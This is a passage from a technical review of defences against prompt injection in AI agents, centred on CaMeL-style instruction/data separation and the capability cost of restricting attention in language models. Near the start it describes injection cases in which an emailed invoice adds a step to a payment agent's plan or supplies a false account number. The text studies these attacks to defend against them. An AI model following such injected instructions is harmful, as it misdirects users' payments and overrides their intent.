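Multi-CaMeL addresses the gap between agents by sending instructions and data separately, so that the receiving planner sees only the instructions. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. The benchmark's attacks rarely exploited this gap, so the demonstration is better evidence of the problem than the 0.2% success rate. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer tasks, though only modestly fewer with the strongest models.

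Peters-Gill and colleagues ran all their CaMeL agents without policies on the data that tools receive. Without such policies, multi-CaMeL prevents an invoice from adding a step to the payment agent's plan, but the invoice can still supply a false account number.

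## What restricted attention costs in capability

Policy checks on agents can roughly halve the number of tasks they complete. Masking attention inside the model would affect capability differently, and the best large-scale evidence of how comes from developers who restrict attention for speed. Full attention compares every position with every earlier one, so doubling the length of a text roughly quadruples the computation. The KV cache also grows with every token. Many open models therefore restrict most layers to part of the text, and some developers have trained matching models with full attention for comparison.

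### What each design lets a position read

*Mistral 7B* (2023) describes a model in which each layer attends to a sliding window of 4,096 tokens. Stacking these layers gives the model a theoretical reach of about 131,000 tokens. Most later models mix windowed layers with full-attention layers, a practice that *InfiX-V1* traces to GPT-3 (2020).

| Design | What a position reads in one layer | How a distant token can still affect it |
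|---|---|---|
| Full attention | Every earlier position | Directly |
| Sliding window | The most recent positions | Through positions in between, over several layers |
| Factored attention | Recent positions, or every hundredth earlier one | In two steps |
| Learned sparse attention | A few tokens or blocks with the highest scores | Directly, if selected |
| Recurrent state | A fixed-size summary of everything earlier | Through the summary |

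Factored attention splits one long jump into two steps. Suppose position 5,000 needs information from the token at position 1,234. In one layer, position 1,300 reads that token, which is 66 places back. In the next, position 5,000 can read position 1,300 because the distance between them, 3,700, is a multiple of 100. Recent open models tend to use the other designs.

Block-sparse attention divides the text into blocks and reads only some of them. A fixed rule can choose the blocks, but newer models learn which ones to read. *MiniMax Sparse Attention* (Lai, Xu and colleagues, 2026) describes a small scoring component that compares the current position with all earlier ones and selects 16 blocks of 128 tokens. The main attention then reads at most 2,048 tokens, which can come from anywhere in the text.

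In Gated DeltaNet, a common type of recurrent layer, the state in each head is a matrix $S$. Merrill, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Olmo Hybrid*, use the form

$$S_t=\alpha_t S_{t-1}(I-2\beta_t k_tk_t^\top)+v_tk_t^\top,\qquad y_t=S_tq_t.$$

The first term shrinks the matrix's old contents and changes what it holds under keys similar to $k_t$. The second stores the value $v_t$ under $k_t$. Multiplying the matrix by a query $q_t$ retrieves values whose keys are similar to $q_t$. One such layer in the 7-billion-parameter model stores about 0.55 million numbers, however long the text is. A full-attention layer of comparable size stores 268 million for a text of 32,000 tokens.

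### Small losses on short texts, larger ones on long texts

Google's *Gemma 3 Technical Report* (2025) found that the ratio of windowed to full layers had little effect on perplexity, even at seven to one. In tests on 2-billion-parameter models, much shorter windows also made little difference. Gemma 3 uses five windowed layers for each full one, with windows of 1,024 tokens.

Very short windows can do more harm. *Sliding Window Recurrences for Sequence Models* (2025) compared 1.3-billion-parameter models trained on 100 billion tokens. Windows of 2,048 tokens gave about the same quality as full attention, but windows of 128 raised perplexity by 5.12. In *RATTENTION* (2025), which trained 3-billion-parameter models on 400 billion tokens, shorter windows lowered scores on MMLU, a broad knowledge test. Adding a recurrent summary of the text outside the window brought those scores back to the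 level of full attention when the window was at least 512 tokens.

Perplexity is a poor guide to how much capability a model loses from restricted attention, because nearby text is enough to predict most words. The Allen Institute for AI's *Olmo 3* (2025) describes a model with 4,096-token attention windows in three of every four layers. Bertsch, Soldaini and colleagues later tested this pattern on 26 models with 7 to 8 billion parameters in *Cracks in the Foundation* (2026). They trained each model on the same 140 billion tokens, then on 10 billion more from long texts. Training loss before the long-text stage explained only 29% of the variation in long-text scores.

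The table shows how two pairs of these models score on HELMET, a set of long-text tasks that includes question answering and retrieval. The models in each pair differ only in their windows. Both models in the second pair use grouped-query attention, in which several heads share stored keys and values to save memory.

| Model | 8K tokens | 16K | 32K | 64K |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No sharing, full attention | 57.7 | 54.3 | 48.7 | 39.7 |
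| No sharing, mostly windows | 58.4 | 52.5 | 47.5 | 41.1 |
| Shared keys and values, full attention | 57.8 | 54.5 | 52.4 | 48.4 |
| Shared keys and values, mostly windows | 54.1 | 49.1 | 44.8 | 36.1 |

On average, attention windows alone lowered scores by one to two points at 32K tokens. This drop is hard to distinguish from chance, because changing only the random starting weights shifted long-text scores by about 8% of their range, or roughly two points here. In models with shared keys and values, windows lowered scores by about nine points. More training on long texts did not close the gaps between architectures. After 50 billion tokens of this training, the worst design still scored lower than the Llama 3 design did after one billion.

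### Larger models, code and reasoning

*The MiniMax-M2 Series* (2026) reports a similar pattern in a model with 230 billion parameters. The developers converted some of its layers to windowed attention and continued training for hundreds of billions to trillions of tokens. MMLU scores were 85.6 with windows and 85.5 without, and mathematics scores were identical. On RULER, which tests whether a model can find and combine items in a long text, scores on two tasks did not fall at 32K tokens. At 128K, one fell from 90 to 72 and the other from 99 to 93. Translation using reference material in the prompt also got worse, with one score falling from 44.8 to 27.2.

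After fine-tuning, the windowed model did as well as the original on competition mathematics (86.7% for both) but fixed fewer software bugs (50.2% against 54.7%). On agent tasks, the score fell from 32.5 to 21.0 in a customer-service test for a telecoms company but rose from 62.3 to 67.5 in one for a retailer.

*GLM-5* (2026) compares several designs on a 9-billion-parameter model with 40 layers. The developers replaced half of the full-attention layers and trained each version on another 190 billion tokens. RepoQA tests whether a model can find a particular function in a large body of code.

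| Replacement for half of the layers | RULER, 64K | RULER, 128K | RepoQA, 128K |
|---|---|---|---|
| None (full attention) | 85.4 | 75.3 | 65.8 |
| Windows in every other layer | 65.9 | 44.9 | 39.3 |
| Windows in layers chosen by search | 83.7 | 69.6 | 51.2 |
| Gated DeltaNet | 76.8 | 64.0 | 56.2 |
| Simplified Gated DeltaNet | 81.8 | 67.0 | 58.5 |

Choosing the positions of the full-attention layers by search, instead of alternating them with restricted layers, recovered most of the performance lost on RULER but only about half of that lost on code retrieval. These comparisons somewhat favour full attention, because each restricted model was adapted from weights trained without restrictions.

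Xiaomi's *MiMo-V2-Flash Technical Report* (2026) avoids this problem by training every version from scratch, and its results are much more favorable to windowed attention. The models had 32 billion parameters and trained on 250 billion tokens, then on 40 billion more with longer texts.

| Test | Full attention | Mixed, 128-token windows | Mixed, 512-token windows |
|---|---|---|---|
| MMLU | 57.3 | 58.3 | 58.3 |
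| RULER, 32K | 89.4 | 89.4 | 84.7 |
| NoLiMa (retrieval without matching words) | 49.7 | 51.2 | 38.5 |
| MRCR (retrieval from long conversations) | 32.5 | 34.4 | 19.6 |

After fine-tuning for reasoning, the model with 128-token windows averaged 46.3% on mathematics, science and programming, compared with 42.4% for full attention. Xiaomi's researchers hypothesise that very short windows force the full-attention layers to specialise in distant text, while longer windows make this division of work less clear. They note that the results may depend on their setup.

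The windows also needed a small change to the softmax, called an attention sink. Ordinary attention weights must add up to one, so a head has to read something in its window even when nothing there is relevant. The sink adds a learned number $b$ to the competition:

$$s_{ij}=\frac{e^{a_{ij}}}{e^{b}+\sum_{j'}e^{a_{ij'}}}.$$

When $b$ is much larger than all the scores $a_{ij}$, the head reads almost nothing. Without the sink, the model with 128-token windows scored only 54.9 on MMLU.

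Xiaomi's results conflict with MiniMax's less than they seem to. Xiaomi's RULER comparison stopped at 32K tokens, and MiniMax also found no loss on RULER at that length. The finished MiMo-V2-Flash model retrieves facts almost perfectly at up to 256K tokens, but there is no equivalent full-attention model to compare it with. Xiaomi kept the 128-token windows in its next model, according to *MiMo-V2.6* (2026).

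Restricted attention can make a model's answers to reasoning problems longer as well as less accurate. *Prefix Sliding for efficient test-time scaling* (2026) tested a sliding-window method on problems from the 2025 AIME mathematics competition. With windows of 8,192 tokens, accuracy was 35.8%, compared with 34.2% for full attention, and answers were about equally long. With windows of 2,048 tokens, accuracy fell to 27.7% and the average answer grew from about 19,000 tokens to 48,000. With the shorter windows, the model still produced text almost 20 times as fast at a length of 128K tokens.

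### Why copying and distant retrieval suffer

A recurrent layer has to fit everything it will need into a fixed amount of memory. If the state has $B$ bits, it can take at most $2^B$ values. A vocabulary of $V$ tokens allows $V^n$ different texts of $n$ tokens. If a model must reproduce a text from the state alone, and always gives the same output for the same state, it can copy at most a share

$$\frac{2^B}{V^n}$$

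of those texts correctly. Copying all of them requires $n\le B/\log_2 V$. Jelassi and others used the fixed size of the state in 2024 to explain why recurrent models copy less well than transformers, which can look up the original tokens.

This limit is very loose for current models. At 16 bits per number, one recurrent layer of Olmo Hybrid holds about 8.8 million bits. That would be enough to store a text of about 530,000 tokens with a vocabulary of 100,000, yet recurrent models fail at much shorter lengths. In *Kronecker Delta Rule for Long Context Linear Attention* (2026), a purely recurrent model found a fact hidden in a text 74.0% of the time at 4K tokens but only 2.6% at 32K. A newer design raised accuracy to 99.6% at 4K but only 5.6% at 32K.

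The way these layers store information probably explains much of the gap. In Olmo Hybrid, the keys in each head have 96 dimensions, so at most 96 of them can be at right angles. With more keys than that, some must overlap, and a query for one value also retrieves parts of others. The layer must also store or discard information before the user's question arrives. Merrill and colleagues tested this on small models that had to look up one bit in a list. With 128 bits, the recurrent model was right 67.6% of the time (guessing would give 50%), while the transformer was nearly perfect.

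Attention windows create a similar difficulty. A fact outside the window can reach a later position only if positions in between pass it along, before it is clear that the fact will be needed. *Shared KV Heads, Sliding Windows, and Vocabulary Size* (2026) found that the first version of Mistral 7B stopped retrieving facts at a distance between 4,089 and 4,098 tokens, almost exactly its window size, although information could in theory travel 131,000 tokens.

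Learned sparse attention largely avoids both problems because it keeps a separate entry for each earlier token and searches these entries when a question arrives. Lai and colleagues trained a 109-billion-parameter model on 3 trillion tokens and found that it performed about as well as one with full attention. At a length of one million tokens, the sparse model needed 28.4 times less computation for attention.

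DeepSeek Sparse Attention, another learned method, can select the wrong tokens, so *GLM-5* overstates its reliability when it calls the method "lossless by construction". In the developers' test, the score on RULER at 128K fell from 79.2 to 71.4 when they trained only the component that selects tokens. Training the whole model for another 150 billion tokens reduced the drop to 0.35 points.

### What newer hybrids have changed

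Combining recurrent layers with some full attention removes much of the retrieval problem. In the list test, Merrill and colleagues' hybrid made no errors. It also did well at tracking variables through a series of swaps, a task the plain transformer failed as the series grew longer.

Olmo Hybrid replaces the windowed-attention layers of Olmo 3 7B with Gated DeltaNet and keeps the full-attention layers. On RULER at 64K tokens it scored 76.9, compared with 70.9 for Olmo 3 with the same context-extension method. It also reached Olmo 3's MMLU accuracy with 49% fewer training tokens. On code it was behind after the main training (17.1 against 19.6) but slightly ahead after the next stage (32.9 against 32.1). The two training runs differed in some other ways, and the results compare recurrence with windowed attention, not with full attention in every layer.

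### Whether the low cost carries over to isolation

Olmo 3 7B has 32 layers, of which 24 use windowed attention and eight use full attention. The last layer uses full attention, so the position that produces the answer can read directly from every earlier position, including those that hold a stranger's email. *ArchSpace* (2026) reports the same three-to-one pattern for Qwen3.5, with recurrent layers in place of windowed ones. Developers keep these long-range paths on purpose. For example, *Muse Glimmer 30B* (2026) says that its mix of local and full layers limits the cache "while preserving long-range information flow".

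An isolating mask has to remove exactly the paths that keep the loss of capability small in these models. It may also hide the text that the task depends on most, such as an emailed invoice, even if that text comes right after the owner's request, whereas a window hides distant text, which is usually less useful for predicting the next word.

The speed experiments give some reason to expect that models can learn well when trained with a mask. Xiaomi's models learned general knowledge and reasoning well even though many of their layers could attend to only 128 tokens. Adding a mask to a finished model is riskier. When the GLM developers put attention windows in every other layer without further training, the model's RULER score at 8K tokens fell from 93.7 to 54.0.

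Limiting attention to a window in every layer comes closer to blocking information flow completely, but only between positions that are far enough apart. *MesaNet* (2025) compared such models, with windows as short as four tokens, with a transformer that could read 2,048. Scores on several common-sense tests differed only marginally, while scores on reading comprehension and on predicting the last word of a passage rose as the windows grew. With a window of four, even 24 layers would reach only 73 positions, so the model would lose the beginning of any longer passage. The common-sense scores probably differed so little because those tests require little context.

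*Sliding-window beats linear attention* (2026) limited Qwen3-8B to attention windows of 64 tokens without retraining it. The model's average score on six short tests fell only from 72.5 to 71.6, though its MMLU score fell from 74.9 to 70.8. Information could still travel about 2,270 positions across the model's 36 layers, enough to cover many short questions.

None of these comparisons removes every path from a marked passage to an answer while leaving the rest of the text readable. Some experiments outside this line of work come closer. Scores fell when Kontonis and colleagues let only written summaries carry earlier reasoning forward, and when Ikeda and colleagues had the model read each document separately. But neither group retrained its model for the stricter condition, so the lasting drop in scores may be smaller.

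Researchers could directly measure how much restricted attention reduces general ability by training two models of the same size on the same data, one of them with a mask that blocks marked passages in every layer. They would then compare the two models on tasks that don't need those passages.
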